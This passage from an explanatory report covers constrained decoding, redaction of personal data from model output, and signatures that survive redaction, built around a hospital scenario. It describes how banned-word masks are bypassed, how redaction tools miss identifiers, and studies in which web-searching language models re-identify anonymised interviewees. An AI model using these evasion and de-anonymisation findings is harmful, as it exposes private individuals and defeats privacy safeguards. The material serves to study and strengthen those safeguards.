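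Park and colleagues therefore estimate it from earlier responses. Their algorithm, ASAp, begins as ordinary masking. After each response, it uses the amount of probability the mask removed at each step to lower its estimates of c for the tokens that led there. Once the model has written 00000, for example, the estimate for an initial 0 is close to zero. The estimates approach the true values as the number of responses grows, but on some problems they had barely improved after 2,000 responses.

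Matching the model's own probabilities more closely did not always produce better answers. On one programming problem, ASAp found a correct solution in 1,588 of 2,000 attempts, compared with 12 for ordinary masking. On another, ASAp found 69 correct solutions and ordinary masking found 363. Geng and colleagues found that masking slightly improved a Llama model's accuracy on school mathematics, from 80.1% to between 81.6% and 83.8%, in a format that let the model reason freely before answering. But *Thinking Before Constraining* (2026) cites several studies in which masking made models worse at certain tasks.

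Later methods try to correct the odds faster.

- **Backing up after an error.** *Approximately Aligned Decoding* (2024) points out that ordinary masking goes back one token when it meets a forbidden one, while ASAp starts again from the beginning. Its own method usually goes back to a recent point where the model was unsure.
- **Discarding invalid responses.** A program can let the model write freely and throw away whatever breaks the format. This gives exactly the right probabilities but can waste over 99% of the work. Parys and colleagues keep the exactness and rule out every dead end they pass, which in their software-testing experiments cut the waste to 70–95% after 100 attempts.
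- **Predicting c.** Özgü, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *The Parser Already Knows*, train a small model to estimate c from the parser's current state. It needs 1,000 sample responses per grammar and at most five minutes of training. A simple version came closer to the correct probabilities than ordinary masking on 12 of 14 grammars, and took 2.5 seconds per response, compared with 3.0 for masking and 16.6 for ASAp. On four database queries it did better on three.
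- **Retraining the model.** *GrammarRL* (2026) trains the model itself to suit the grammar, and scored an average of 9.8 points higher than masking that always picks the most probable allowed token. The hospital would then be using a different model from the one it had tested.

### Banned words

Some developers use masking to keep certain words out of free text, often through the logit bias setting. This is much less reliable than enforcing a format.

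Suppose the hospital wants to stop a model from recommending aspirin, and bans the token `aspirin`. The model can still write `asp` followed by `irin`, because different sequences of tokens can spell the same text, as Bhat and colleagues note. The word has seven letters, so it can be split or left whole at each of the six gaps between letters. If every possible piece were a token, there would be 2^6 = 64 ways to write the word, and the ban would block one of them.

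A mask that works on characters can block all 64 ways of splitting "aspirin" into tokens. But it doesn't block "Aspirin", "a-s-p-i-r-i-n", misspellings or "acetylsalicylic acid", another name for the same drug, unless the list includes them. The model could also name the drug in another language or describe it without naming it, and no list can include every possible phrasing.

Longer lists also block more harmless text. A ban on the letters "die" removes "diet". The mask can also change the meaning of a sentence because it acts in the middle of a word. If the model has written "Stop aspir" and the mask blocks `in`, the next most likely token may be `ation`, and the doctor reads "Stop aspiration before surgery".

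A list of permitted values works better where the output has a fixed field. If the schema limits the drug field to the names of drugs the pharmacy stocks, no other drug can appear there under any spelling, although it can still appear in a comments field. The list also needs an entry such as "none of these", because otherwise the model has to name a wrong drug when the right one is not listed.

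## How much does redacting text remove, and what can it distort?

A good redaction tool removes most of the names and numbers from ordinary text, but the remaining text is often enough to identify the person. Rewriting the text hides more, but also removes much information that nobody needed to hide. Both methods can change what a sentence means.

### Finding and replacing identifiers

Suppose the hospital's model writes "Call Anna Lee on 555-0142. Tom Lee is Anna Lee's brother." *Redacting Personal Data* (2026) describes a typical procedure for redacting text before it is sent to a language model, and the same steps work on a model's output.

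1. The software searches for people it already knows about. The hospital's records link this note to Anna Lee, so it can look for her name directly.
2. Patterns find text with a fixed format, such as three digits, a hyphen and four more digits.
3. A tagger finds names the hospital did not know in advance, such as Tom Lee. It is a model trained to label each token as part of a name, an address and so on, or as ordinary text.
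4. The software merges overlapping finds and replaces them.

Some systems add a language model to look for sensitive details that have no fixed form. The replacement itself can also take several forms.

| Replacement | Result |
|---|---|
| Deletion | Call on. is 's brother. |
| One label per category | Call PERSON on PHONE. PERSON is PERSON's brother. |
| Numbered pseudonyms | Call PERSON_1 on PHONE_1. PERSON_2 is PERSON_1's brother. |
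| Invented values | Call Maria Costa on 555-0199. Paul Costa is Maria Costa's brother. |

When a redaction tool uses a single label for each category, readers can't tell people apart. In April, OpenAI (2026) released Privacy Filter, a free tagger small enough to run on a laptop. In OpenAI's example, an email from Maya Chen to Jordan, the tool replaces both names with PRIVATE_PERSON. It also replaces the date of a product launch with PRIVATE_DATE, although that date identifies nobody.

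Numbered pseudonyms let readers tell people apart, and the software can restore the names if it stores a map from each pseudonym to the original. *LLM-Redactor* (2026) warns that a crash can destroy the map, after which nobody can restore the response. Invented values read most naturally, but a reader may not realise they are invented.

### What current tools catch

Recall is the share of real identifiers that a tool finds, and precision is the share of the items it flags that are real identifiers. The table combines OpenAI's measurements with results from two papers. *OpenAI Privacy Filter* (Uppala, 2026) tested OpenAI's tool on 32 benchmarks, and *PIIBench* (2026) tested several tools, including Microsoft's widely used Presidio.

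| Tool | Text | Recall | Precision | Reported by |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Privacy Filter | Synthetic text in six languages | 98.0% | 94.0% | OpenAI |
| Privacy Filter | Passwords and keys in program code | 96.5% | 74.7% | OpenAI |
| Privacy Filter | Synthetic medical consultations | 81.8% | 32.4% | Uppala |
| Privacy Filter | English financial text | 49.0% | 63.8% | Uppala |
| GPT-4o | Synthetic medical consultations | 94.9% | 56% | Uppala |
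| Presidio | Mixture of public datasets | 12.7% | 15.2% | *PIIBench* |

(The precision for GPT-4o follows from its recall and the combined score that Uppala reports.)

The results differ partly because the testers counted differently. OpenAI's figures are for tokens, while Uppala and *PIIBench* required an exact match. Under exact matching, a tool that marks "Anna" instead of "Anna Lee" scores one miss and one false alarm. The medical test also counts only the details of the person asking the question, so a tool loses precision each time it correctly finds someone else's name. Still, a hospital should expect results closer to the medical rows than to the first one. *GLiNER2-PII* (2026) reports recall of only 68.1% on medical text for its own tagger, which had the best combined score in its comparison.

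Benchmarks also disagree about what counts as an identifier. In *Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels*, Hsu and Berlin (2026) had a language model relabel two benchmarks under one set of definitions. In the first, 59–86% of the labelled examples in five categories, including passport and credit card numbers, no longer qualified. For example, the benchmark had labelled a passport number in "Don't forget to bring your YV9022888!", which doesn't mention a passport. In the second, 29% of the internet addresses were newly labelled, almost all of them inside longer web addresses.

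A tagger's recall depends heavily on context. OpenAI measured recall of 86.3% when a clue such as "my home number is" came just before the identifier, 70.5% when it came just after, and 58.4% when there was no clue. For phone numbers alone, removing the clue reduced recall from 91.9% to 31.8%. Recall was 63.1% for identifiers with unusual spacing and 67.4% for numbers spelled out in words.

Older tools do worst on the most sensitive details. In the *REDACT* benchmark (2026), Presidio found 7% of them, compared with 74% for GPT-4.1 and 77% for Claude Sonnet 4.6. Presidio found only 2% of partial mentions.

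A hospital can improve a tagger by training it further on the hospital's own reports. OpenAI further trained a tagger on a tenth of the training examples from a set of medical and legal questions, which raised recall from 79.5% to 96.0% and precision from 41.4% to 96.3%.

### Fifty identifiers in one report

Even a redaction tool with high recall leaves identifiers in many documents. If the tool finds each identifier with probability r, and its errors are independent, it finds all n identifiers in a document with probability rⁿ. For r = 0.99 and n = 50, this is 0.605, so about 395 of 1,000 such documents would still contain at least one identifier.

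| Recall | Average number missed out of 50 | Chance that the report is fully clean |
|---|---|---|
| 95% | 2.5 | 8% |
| 98% | 1 | 36% |
| 99% | 0.5 | 60% |
| 99.98% | 0.01 | 99% |

Real errors are not independent. If the 50 identifiers are five names that appear ten times each, and the tool finds either every copy of a name or none, the chance of a clean report is 0.99⁵, or about 95%. But each missed name then remains in the report ten times. OpenAI warns that taggers tend to miss uncommon names and regional naming conventions. The failures are therefore also likely to affect the same people repeatedly, so a tool with 99% recall overall could miss one patient's name in every report.

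A redaction tool can miss copies of a patient's name in unusual places. It may find "Anna Lee" in 49 sentences of a report but miss `lee_anna_scan.pdf` in a list of attachments. Its recall for that report is 98%, but the patient's name is still there. The hospital should therefore search all other fields and filenames for every value the tool finds, along with likely variants.

A single code left in a text can reveal a lot, as an experiment on immune-cell receptors shows. In *Auditing Tool Traces in Agentic LLMs*, Liu, Li and colleagues (2026) studied a model that used the results of five software tools to predict whether a receptor would bind to a target. The model scored 0.81 on a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. But one tool's result included a filename containing a database code for the protein structure, and another tool's result contained the same code. When the researchers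 replaced the code in every field, the score fell to 0.50. Replacing the target's sequence in the same way had no effect. The model had apparently been relying on the codes, which happened to correlate with the right answers. Removing the code only from the filename would have left the other copy in place.

Copies of a secret can also remain in fields that nobody reads. *Stealing Reasoning Traces from Proprietary LLM APIs* reports 62 API keys (passwords for software services) that would have remained in models' encrypted reasoning even if users had removed every secret from the visible text.

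Testers can avoid some of this confusion by reporting results for whole documents as well as for individual tokens. Politis and Pappas (2026) recommend this in *What Gradients Add to Text Leakage in Split Language Models* for a different kind of leak, in which an observer reconstructs text from a model's internal values. Under one defence, the observer could rebuild almost no documents exactly but still recovered 83–91% of the tokens.

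### What a reader can infer from the rest

Suppose a tool correctly redacts the names, numbers and addresses in a report, leaving the sentence "PERSON_1, who won an Olympic medal in rowing before becoming a heart surgeon, has diabetes." Very few people fit that description, and a web search might identify PERSON_1.

*RedacBench* (Jeon, Kim and Shin, 2026) measures what a reader can still infer from a text after redaction. It breaks 514 texts, mostly emails from the energy company Enron and from Hillary Clinton's time as US Secretary of State, into 8,053 propositions, which are small facts that a reader can infer whether or not the text states them. For instance, if someone mentions attending a meeting at a company, one proposition might be that they work there. Each text comes with one or more of 187 confidentiality policies, which determine the propositions that are sensitive.

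The security score is the share of sensitive propositions that a reader can no longer infer after redaction. The utility score is the share of other propositions that a reader can still infer. If a report has four sensitive propositions and six others, and redaction stops a reader from inferring three of each, its security is 75% and its utility is 50%.

Jeon and colleagues tested eleven language models with two methods. In masking, the model removes the words that violate the policy. In adversarial redaction, it first lists the sensitive facts it finds in the text and then rewrites the text in more general terms to hide them. The model can repeat the listing and rewriting on its own result.

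| Method | Security, across eleven models | Utility, across eleven models |
|---|---|---|
| Masking | 36–52% | 73–85% |
| Adversarial redaction, one round | 47–72% | 49–75% |
| Adversarial redaction, two rounds | 57–81% | 38–65% |

GPT-5-mini reached the highest security score, 80.9%, after two rounds, but it kept only 37.6% of the harmless information. Extra rounds can partly make up for a weaker model. GPT-4.1-mini after seven rounds slightly outperformed GPT-5 after two.

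One of the emails recommends an employee for an award because she covered for a colleague on leave, working seven days a week for about two months. It adds that her information was critical that year partly because of a pipeline explosion. In the first round of adversarial redaction, the model changed the explosion to "operational challenges" and the long weeks to "exceptional dedication". It didn't remove the names of the sender and recipient until the second round.

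The absolute scores depend heavily on which model judges what a reader could infer. Jeon and colleagues used GPT-4.1-mini, which scored GPT-4.1's masked texts at 36.4% for security and 82.0% for utility. GPT-5 scored the same texts at 86.6% and 36.8%, because it applied a stricter standard for what counts as inferable. The three methods ranked in the same order under every judge, so the ranking is more reliable than any single percentage. Texts that the researchers redacted by hand scored 62.8% for security and 85.2% for utility. The best masking result at about the same utility scored only 35.9% for security, which means much of the loss is avoidable.

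*LLM Censorship* (2023) used a theorem from computer science to show that no procedure can correctly decide, for every program a model might write, whether the program does something forbidden. A filter that judges programs by what they do therefore can't be perfect in general.

### Naming people in redacted interviews

Language models with web search make this kind of inference easy. To measure the risk, Wen and Li (2026), in *AgentDoxx*, built 822 synthetic interviews from public facts about real people who had identified themselves on Reddit. They removed direct identifiers and asked models to name the interviewee. The five best configurations were right 47–48% of the time. Three models with downloadable weights named 15–28% of the people without search, from what they had learned in training.

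The researchers then tested defences on 143 interviews, each of which at least one of twelve attacking configurations had already solved.

| Defence | Average success of the attackers |
|---|---|
| No further redaction | 75.1% |
| Masking names and similar items with Presidio | 62.0% |
| Masking, then paraphrasing | 45.9% |
| Removing phrases that a trained model marks as identifying | 35.1% |
| Replacing identifying facts with false ones | 34.2% |
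| Instructing the attacking model not to identify anyone | 21.6% |

After Presidio masked the interviews, at least one attacker still named the right person in 85.3% of them. Presidio had changed only 0.42% of the characters, because most of the clues were ordinary descriptions of jobs and projects. The instruction in the last row works only if the attacker chooses to include it. Even then, in 37% of the cases where the model withheld a name, it had already found the right name in its searches.

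A failed identification can also do harm. When the right person appeared in the search results but the model gave a different answer, it named the wrong person 81.6% of the time.

More careful rewriting protects speakers' identities better. The method in *LLM Anonymization Against Agentic Re-Identification* (Li, Wen and Li, 2026) first uses a model with web search to find details that could identify the speaker. It then marks the phrases that reveal those details, generates several sets of replacements and picks the set that leaks least. The researchers tested it on 53 real interviews whose speakers an earlier attack had identified. Three attacking models identified 26 to 40 of the speakers after redaction with Presidio, 10 to 12 after the method from which Jeon and colleagues adapted adversarial redaction, and 0 to 7 after the new method. The rewritten interviews kept 72–76% of the information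 the researchers wanted to preserve, measured as pairs that link a fact about a speaker to something the speaker said.

These interviews were unusually easy to identify, so the rates don't apply to typical text. Text published today will also be exposed to later models, which may identify more people. On the 143 *AgentDoxx* interviews before further redaction, GPT-4.1 Mini (April 2025) used web search and named 42.0% of the people. GPT-5.6 Terra (July 2026) named 95.1% at its highest reasoning setting.

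### Redacting an agent's record

An agent's record lists the tools it used, the results and the order of the steps. Customers and auditors need this to check the work, but it can also reveal the owner's trade secrets, such as a formula for ranking drugs. Xu, He and Fung (2026), in *REDACT*, propose a way to hide the secrets and keep the evidence. (Their system, RedAct for short, is unrelated to the benchmark of the same name.)

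A language model reads the owner's private instructions and lists the formulas, thresholds and methods to protect. A person removes duplicates from the list. A second model then rewrites the record, replacing those items with general descriptions while keeping the final answer, the evidence of tool use and the order of the steps.

On 75 long tasks, RedAct removed 70.6% of the protected items. Final answers, tool names, verification paths and data field names survived at 91.0–96.6% of their original level. Xu and colleagues also tested whether other agents could learn the owner's methods from the records. Without records, these agents passed an average of 68.0% of the checks along each task. With the original records, they passed 71.8–73.7%, depending on how they used them, and with the redacted records, they passed 65.5–67.5%. A model that rewrote the records without the list of secrets left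 much more that agents could reuse.

RedAct has a serious drawback for auditors because it inserts invented steps into some records, such as a harmless check of the computer's settings and its result. These steps let the owner later recognise models trained on the records. They do not change the final answer, but the agent never took them, so an auditor would be reading a partly fictional account. The record also fails the test r' = m(r) unless the announced rule m includes the insertions. Owners have a reason not to announce the insertions, because a copier who knew about them could remove them.

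OWASP recommends a simpler way to limit what a record reveals, which is to log an identifier and a hash of each document an agent retrieves instead of its text. An auditor who has the original document can then confirm which version the agent read. Some evidence also survives ordinary redaction. *When Only the Final Text Survives* (2026) describes a method that hides a signal in the wording as several agents write, to show later which agent wrote which part. Replacing names and email addresses with labels barely affected the method's accuracy.

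### Five sentences that change their meaning

The sentences below are invented, but each error could happen in an ordinary redaction system.

| Original | What the reader sees | Cause |
|---|---|---|
| Denies chest pain. | Chest pain. | The tagger took "Denies" for the name Denise, and the software deleted it |
| Prednisolone 5/10 mg on alternate days. | Prednisolone 8/10 mg on alternate days. | The software took "5/10" for 5 October and moved all dates by three days |
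| Fit to drive until 3 March. | Fit to drive. | The tagger marked "until" as part of the date, and the software deleted both |
| PERSON_1 is allergic to penicillin. | Tom Lee is allergic to penicillin. | PERSON_1 was Anna Lee, but the software restored the name using the map from another report |
| The model found Ms Lee's tumour but missed Mr Park's. | The model found PERSON's tumour. | The model's supplier, who was supposed to hide names, removed an embarrassing clause |

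The doctor would have no reason to doubt any of these results. Labels would have made the first three errors visible. "PERSON chest pain" and "DATE mg" look wrong, so a reader would probably ask for the original. That is a good reason to prefer labels to deletion or invented values in medical text, even though labels are less pleasant to read.

*Locale-Conditioned Few-Shot Prompting Mitigates Demonstration Regurgitation in On-Device PII Substitution* (2026) ran OpenAI's Privacy Filter on 100 synthetic texts and found that dates accounted for 44.5% of the filter's false alarms. OpenAI warns that excess redaction can remove context needed for audits and decisions, and recommends keeping human review for medical and other sensitive work.

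A language model that redacts text by rewriting it may also add information that was not in the original. Jeon and colleagues extracted the facts from texts that GPT-4.1 had redacted and found that the originals did not support 3.36% of them. That rate, about one in thirty, is tolerable in a summary for researchers but not in a list of allergies.

Restoring names to the wrong people is easier to prevent. If every report numbers its people from PERSON_1, software that uses another report's map of labels to names will still find a name to insert. If labels are random and never reused across reports, such as PERSON_7F3A, the other map has no entry for them, and the software can stop without inserting a name. Random labels don't help if the model that processed the text confused two labels and attached the allergy to the wrong one.

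The last row of the table involves no technical error. Whoever redacts a text also decides what readers will believe, and a vague rule gives them more freedom. One *RedacBench* policy covers all "strategic business, financial, operational, legal, and diplomatic information", which could justify removing almost any report of a failure. A rule that replaces each name with a label, and nothing else, would have kept the missed tumour in the sentence. In RedAct, the owner of the agent decides what counts as secret, so an auditor has to trust the party under audit not to hide mistakes. (Cryptography can prove that a redactor removed only permitted parts, but not that the choice was fair.)

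### Redacting a stream

Streaming makes redaction harder because the software has to filter text before the whole response is available. Suppose "555-0142" arrives in two chunks, "555-" and "0142". Neither matches the pattern for a phone number, so a filter that checks each chunk separately lets both through.

The usual remedy is to check each chunk together with the end of the previous one. NVIDIA's *Output Rail Streaming* shows a configuration with chunks of 200 tokens and an overlap of 50. But the overlap only helps the filter detect the number, and the software cannot take back "555-" if it has already sent it.

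To prevent this, the software has to hold some text back. If the longest secret has L characters, an incomplete one can take up at most the last L − 1 characters received. The software can therefore hold back that many, release the text before them, and check again when more arrives. For a 40-character key, the reader would be 39 characters behind the model, which is hardly noticeable.

Some products offer a faster mode that sends text first and checks it afterwards. With NVIDIA's `stream_first` setting, the stream stops with an error when the filter finds a violation, but the user has already received everything up to that point. AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content* describes a similar choice between a synchronous mode, which checks each chunk before sending it and so adds a delay, and an asynchronous mode, which sends chunks immediately. AWS warns that the asynchronous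 mode does not support masking sensitive information.

Holding back a fixed number of characters works only for secrets of limited length, and a description that identifies someone may build up over several paragraphs. Jeon and colleagues had GPT-4.1-nano redact texts one chunk at a time, with access to earlier chunks but not later ones. Its security score fell from 64.1% to 55.2%, because some details became sensitive only in light of later text. A hospital that needs to redact such descriptions has to wait for the complete response before showing the doctor any of it.

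## Can a redacted output still be authenticated?

A reader can authenticate a redacted output if the signer used a signature designed for redaction. With an ordinary signature, any change makes the check fail, so the reader cannot tell from the failure whether a hospital deleted a full stop or an attacker changed "benign" to "malignant".

### Who signs, and when

A hospital that has only ordinary signatures can arrange the work in three ways.

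| Order of work | What the reader can check | Whom the reader must trust |
|---|---|---|
| The provider signs, then the hospital redacts | Nothing, because the signature fails | The hospital, for every word |
| The hospital redacts, then signs the result | That nobody has changed the text since the hospital signed it | The hospital, for every word |
| The provider signs the original, and the hospital signs the redacted version and keeps the original sealed | The same, and an auditor can later compare the two versions | The hospital, until an auditor opens the original |

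The provider could also redact the report before signing it. The reader would then need to trust only the provider, whose model made the diagnosis anyway. But the provider would need to know in advance what each reader may see. If a research registry, an insurer and a second hospital may each see different fields, the provider has to make and sign three versions.

Keeping a sealed original is the best of the three options in the table, and the signed receipts in Guan's AEX work in a similar way. But a sealed original mainly deters dishonest redaction, because a later audit doesn't help a reader who has to act today. This approach also fails if the hospital loses the original.

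### Removing one block of four

Cryptographers began looking for something better around 2001. *Content Extraction Signatures* (Steinfeld, Bull and Zheng, 2002) describes a scheme in which Alice signs a document, Bob extracts parts of it, and Cathy verifies that those parts came from Alice without seeing the rest. *Sanitizable Signatures* (Ateniese, Chou and colleagues, 2005) traces a broader version of the idea to a series of talks by the cryptographer Ronald Rivest, who proposed signatures that allow certain types of "forgery", fixed in advance. Cryptographers call a signature that permits deletions a redactable signature.

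A simple version uses the same kind of hash tree as a public log. Suppose the provider splits a report into four blocks:

- m₁: "Scan of 3 March"
- m₂: "Finding: benign"
- m₃: "Patient number 482913506"
- m₄: "Confidence: low"

The provider signs the report as follows.

1. It picks a separate random value, called a salt, for each block.
2. It hashes each block together with its salt, so that h₁ = H(s₁, m₁), and likewise for the other three.
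3. It combines the hashes in pairs: h₁₂ = H(h₁, h₂) and h₃₄ = H(h₃, h₄).
4. It computes the root, R = H(h₁₂, h₃₄), and signs it.

The hospital receives the four blocks, the four salts and the signature. To remove the patient number, it replaces m₃ and s₃ with the hash h₃. The reader's software computes h₁, h₂ and h₄ from the blocks and salts it received, takes h₃ as given, and works out the root. The root is the same as before, so the provider's signature is still valid.

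The hospital did not need the provider's private key or help. But if it had changed "benign" to "malignant", h₂ would have changed, and with it h₁₂ and the root. It could not have swapped two blocks either, since each hash has a fixed place in the tree. A reader of the redacted version cannot restore the patient number, because the hospital removed both the number and its salt.

The tree also keeps redacted documents small. If the hospital removes blocks 3 and 4, it can send the single hash h₃₄ in place of both. In a record of 1,024 blocks, a redactor who keeps only one block sends ten hashes. If the provider had signed a plain list of hashes instead, the redactor would have to send the hashes of the other 1,023 blocks.

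### Why every block needs its own salt

Without the salt, a reader who knows the wording of the block could recover the patient number from h₃ by hashing "Patient number 000000000", "Patient number 000000001" and so on until one hash matched. A nine-digit number has only a billion possible values, and a modern graphics card can compute more than a billion hashes per second, so the reader would find the match within about a second.

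The salt makes this search infeasible. A salt of 128 random bits has 2^128 (about 3.4 × 10^38) possible values. At a billion hashes per second, trying every salt with a single patient number would take about 10^22 years.

*Selective Disclosure for JSON Web Tokens* (Fett, Yasuda and Campbell, 2025), a proposed internet standard, gives the most detailed advice on salts. It recommends at least 128 random bits per salt and requires a new salt for each item. If the provider used one salt for the whole report, the reader would receive it with the first block and could use it to test every possible patient number in the third. For the same reason, when the hospital removes a block, it has to delete that block's salt too.

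### Hashes in published logs

Some published logs replace text with hashes. *Inspectable AI for Science* (Binkyte, Abuaddba and colleagues, 2026) proposes that scientists who use AI to write papers publish a record of how they used it. The paper demonstrates this with a literature review that a Llama model drafted from human notes. To keep the paper anonymous during peer review, the published log gives only hashes of the full prompts and responses. The description of these hashes doesn't mention a salt.

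Binkyte and colleagues also publish the prompt templates and the input notes. A reviewer could therefore fill in a template with guesses for the missing parts, such as the paper's title, and hash the result. A match would confirm the guess. The text would have to match exactly, down to the spacing, and a long response is much harder to guess than a prompt built from a template. But many organisations reuse nearly identical prompts. If a hospital's log contains the unsalted hash of "Summarise the latest scan of patient 482913506", anyone who knows the wording can recover the number by trying all billion possibilities.

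The remedy is to add a salt to each entry and store the salts privately with the original texts. When an auditor asks about an entry, the hospital supplies the text and its salt. If the hospital loses the salt, it can no longer prove what the entry contained, even if it still has the text.

Salts protect only the log's secrecy. The researcher who used the model also computes the hashes, so the hashes don't prove that the model wrote the response. A dishonest researcher could write a response by hand and log its hash. Binkyte and colleagues acknowledge that someone could alter a log afterwards to misrepresent how they used AI. A provider's signature on each hash would prevent this.

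### Unforgeability, privacy and transparency

Early redactable signatures did not all guarantee the same properties. In *Redactable Signatures for Tree-Structured Data*, Brzuska, Busch and colleagues precisely defined three properties for documents arranged as trees.

Unforgeability means that nobody without the private key can produce a valid signature on a new document, even after obtaining signatures on many documents of their choice. A version made by cutting parts from a signed document does not count as new.

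Privacy means the redacted document and its signature reveal nothing about the content of the removed parts. To test this, an attacker chooses two documents that become identical after redaction, for example two reports that differ only in the patient number. The attacker then receives the redacted version of one of them. The scheme has privacy if the attacker cannot guess which document it came from noticeably more than 50% of the time.

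Transparency is stronger, and means that a reader cannot tell whether anyone removed anything. The attacker receives either a redacted document or a shorter document that the signer signed in that form, and must decide which.

Brzuska and colleagues proved that transparency implies privacy. If a redacted report looks the same as a freshly signed short one, it can't contain clues about the removed text, because the short one never had any. Privacy doesn't imply transparency, because any private scheme can be changed to mark every redacted document as redacted. The removed text stays secret, but the reader knows that something was removed.

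The hash tree above has privacy but not transparency, because the reader sees h₃ where a block should be. In an example from Brzuska and colleagues, a medical record has a gap in the position reserved for an HIV test, so the reader learns that the patient took the test, though not the result. Several gaps in positions associated with one disease may reveal the diagnosis.

Hiding the gaps takes more computation. When many blocks share one parent, the number of signatures in Brzuska and colleagues' transparent scheme grows with the square of the number of blocks, so 100 blocks could take thousands of signatures, while the hash tree needs one. Brzuska and colleagues consider privacy without transparency sufficient when readers already expect redaction, as with reports that have had patients' names removed.

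Transparency also conflicts with output integrity, which requires the hospital to announce its changes. Even without transparency, the hospital can avoid most of the leak in the HIV example by using the same form for everyone, with an HIV field that contains "not tested" when there was no test. A gap in that field then shows only that the hospital withheld it.

### "The lesion is not malignant"

Suppose the provider signs the sentence "The lesion is not malignant" with each word as a separate, removable block. Someone removes the block containing "not" and sends its hash instead. The doctor's software computes the correct root and reports a valid signature. If it then displays the remaining words without marking the gap, the doctor reads "The lesion is malignant".

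The shorter sentence is a permitted redaction, so it does not count as a forgery under the definition above, and no part of the cryptography has failed. There are 2^5 = 32 ways to keep or remove the five words, all with valid signatures. Eight of them keep "malignant" but remove "not".

The easiest protection is to show where text was removed. "The lesion is [removed] malignant" would make most doctors ask what is missing. Ateniese and colleagues consider explicit marks necessary to prevent this kind of attack on meaning. But the signature software can only report the removal, so the program that displays the text has to show it.

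Larger blocks help too. If each sentence is one block, a redactor can keep or remove it but can't reverse its meaning by deleting a word. Removing a whole sentence can still change the meaning of the report. If a report reads "The biopsy found cancer. The laboratory later traced the sample to another patient", removing the second sentence leaves a false diagnosis. Larger blocks also force the hospital to remove more than it needs to, because it can't hide a name without losing any finding in the same block. This is a reason to have the model write names and findings in separate fields.

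In nested data, an item's meaning can also depend on its position. If a scheme allows someone to remove only the heading "Mother's medical history" above "breast cancer", the disease may seem to be the patient's own. *Redactable Signatures for Independent Removal of Structure and Content* (Samelin, Pöhls and colleagues, 2012) describes an attack that changes the meaning of signed tree data, and proposes a scheme that handles removing structure separately from removing content.

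The provider can also forbid the removal of certain blocks. In the four-block report, it could sign the root together with the code 1101, where 1 means a block must stay. The reader's software would then reject any version missing the scan date, the finding or the confidence. Only two versions would remain valid, with and without the patient number. Without such a code, the hospital could also drop "Confidence: low".

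Some redaction rules depend on which parts of the output appear together. A provider might allow the hospital to withhold the finding, but require the confidence to appear whenever the finding does. Researchers have extended both content extraction signatures and hash trees to enforce such rules. Others have designed schemes in which one redactor can forbid later redactors from removing anything more.

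Rules about meaning are harder to enforce. If the rule is "remove only information that identifies the patient", a reader who sees only h₃ cannot tell whether it stands for a patient number or an admission that the model had failed on similar scans. The provider could sign a visible label for each block, such as "patient identifier". The reader would then have to trust the provider's labels, but not the hospital's choice of what to remove. For a simple format, the hospital could instead give a zero-knowledge proof that the hidden block contains the words "Patient number" and nine digits. No comparable proof exists for a vague rule such as "remove sensitive business information", because nobody can state it precisely enough for a program to check.

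### Replacement and accountability

Deletion is not always enough. In an example from Ateniese and colleagues, a study of an epidemic may need the exact dates of treatment, while a cancer study may need only the time between treatments. For the cancer study, the hospital could move all of a patient's dates by the same number of days, but a redactable signature permits only removal.

Their alternative is a sanitizable signature. The signer marks certain blocks as changeable and names a censor, who has a separate private key. Only the censor can put new text in those blocks and produce a valid signature. In a dispute, the signer can prove that the censor made the change.

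This flexibility is also a risk, because the censor can replace "benign" with "malignant" if the finding is in a changeable block, and the signature will still be valid. The signer should therefore make as few blocks changeable as possible, and the reader should know which ones they are. For government documents released under the US Freedom of Information Act, Ateniese and colleagues similarly expect the public to prefer knowing which parts the agency could have changed.

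With a redactable signature, anyone who holds the full document can usually redact it, so the reader cannot tell who removed a block. Pöhls and Samelin combine redactable and sanitizable signatures into a scheme that allows only removal and identifies the party responsible.

Neither redactable nor sanitizable signatures suit RedAct, the system described in *REDACT*, in which an agent's owner rewrites the agent's record to hide trade secrets. A redactable signature would fail because the new wording is not a subset of the original. A sanitizable signature would let the owner rewrite the record freely, but an auditor would still have to trust the owner about the rewritten parts.

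### Credentials that show only some fields

The best-developed practical relative of these schemes is SD-JWT, a standard by Fett and colleagues intended mainly for digital credentials, such as proof of age or address. The issuer signs the credential once, and the holder chooses which fields to show each verifier. Digital driving licences use a similar method.

SD-JWT uses a list of salted hashes rather than a tree. If the provider issued the hospital's report in this format, the signed part might be:

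`{"finding":"benign","_sd":["hash A","hash B"]}`

The finding is always visible. Each of the two hashes stands for a hidden field. To reveal a field, the hospital sends its salt, name and value, such as `["random salt","patient","Anna Lee"]`. The reader's software hashes this and checks that the result is in the signed list. Both the name and the value of a hidden field stay secret, so the reader does not learn that it is called "HIV test".

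The hash covers the field exactly as the issuer encoded it, so SD-JWT needs no canonical form. The issuer should shuffle the list of hashes, because the original order could reveal what the fields are. The number of hashes can also reveal information, for instance if a report contains an extra field only when the patient has a certain disease. The issuer can hide the number of real fields by adding decoys, which are hashes that don't correspond to any field. In one of the standard's examples, an address has four real fields and four decoys.

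The issuer decides which fields the holder may withhold. Fett and colleagues forbid issuers to let holders remove any field that a reader needs to judge whether the credential is valid, such as its expiry date. They also say that the reader's software should check that every field it needs is present, in case the issuer made one removable by mistake. A hospital's software could check for the "confidence" field in the same way.

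The signature protects each field but not the selection of fields. A relay between the hospital and the registry can remove a disclosed field, and the remaining fields will still pass verification. An optional feature called key binding prevents this. The holder signs the selection with its own key, together with the name of the intended reader and a fresh value that prevents replay. The reader then knows it received the selection the holder sent, though the selection itself may be misleading.

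Redaction with SD-JWT also does not stop readers from combining the fields they receive. If the registry receives the patient's age and an insurer receives the postcode, they can tell from the identical signed part that both fields came from the same report. To prevent this, the issuer can supply several copies with different salts and keys, so that the holder uses each copy for only one reader.

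### Redaction in C2PA records

C2PA is a standard for signed records that accompany images, videos and other files and describe their origin and editing. Each record, called a manifest, contains separate statements called assertions. One assertion might identify the camera that took a picture, and another the AI model that changed it.

C2PA's *Implementation Guidance* explains that a program can remove an assertion from an earlier manifest but must record the removal in a new manifest. Docs.rs' *c2pa 0.83.0*, the documentation for a C2PA software library, gives an example. The program finds the assertion that contains the file's metadata, adds its address to a list of redactions, and records a `c2pa.redacted` action that lists the presence of personal information as the reason.

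This design gives up transparency so that readers know about each change, which suits output integrity. A newspaper could remove the location from a photographer's file, and readers would see that it is missing, along with the stated reason. They would have to trust that reason, because they cannot see what was removed. C2PA also describes encryption as an alternative. A program can encrypt the camera details so that only people with the key can read them, whereas nobody can recover a deleted assertion from the file.

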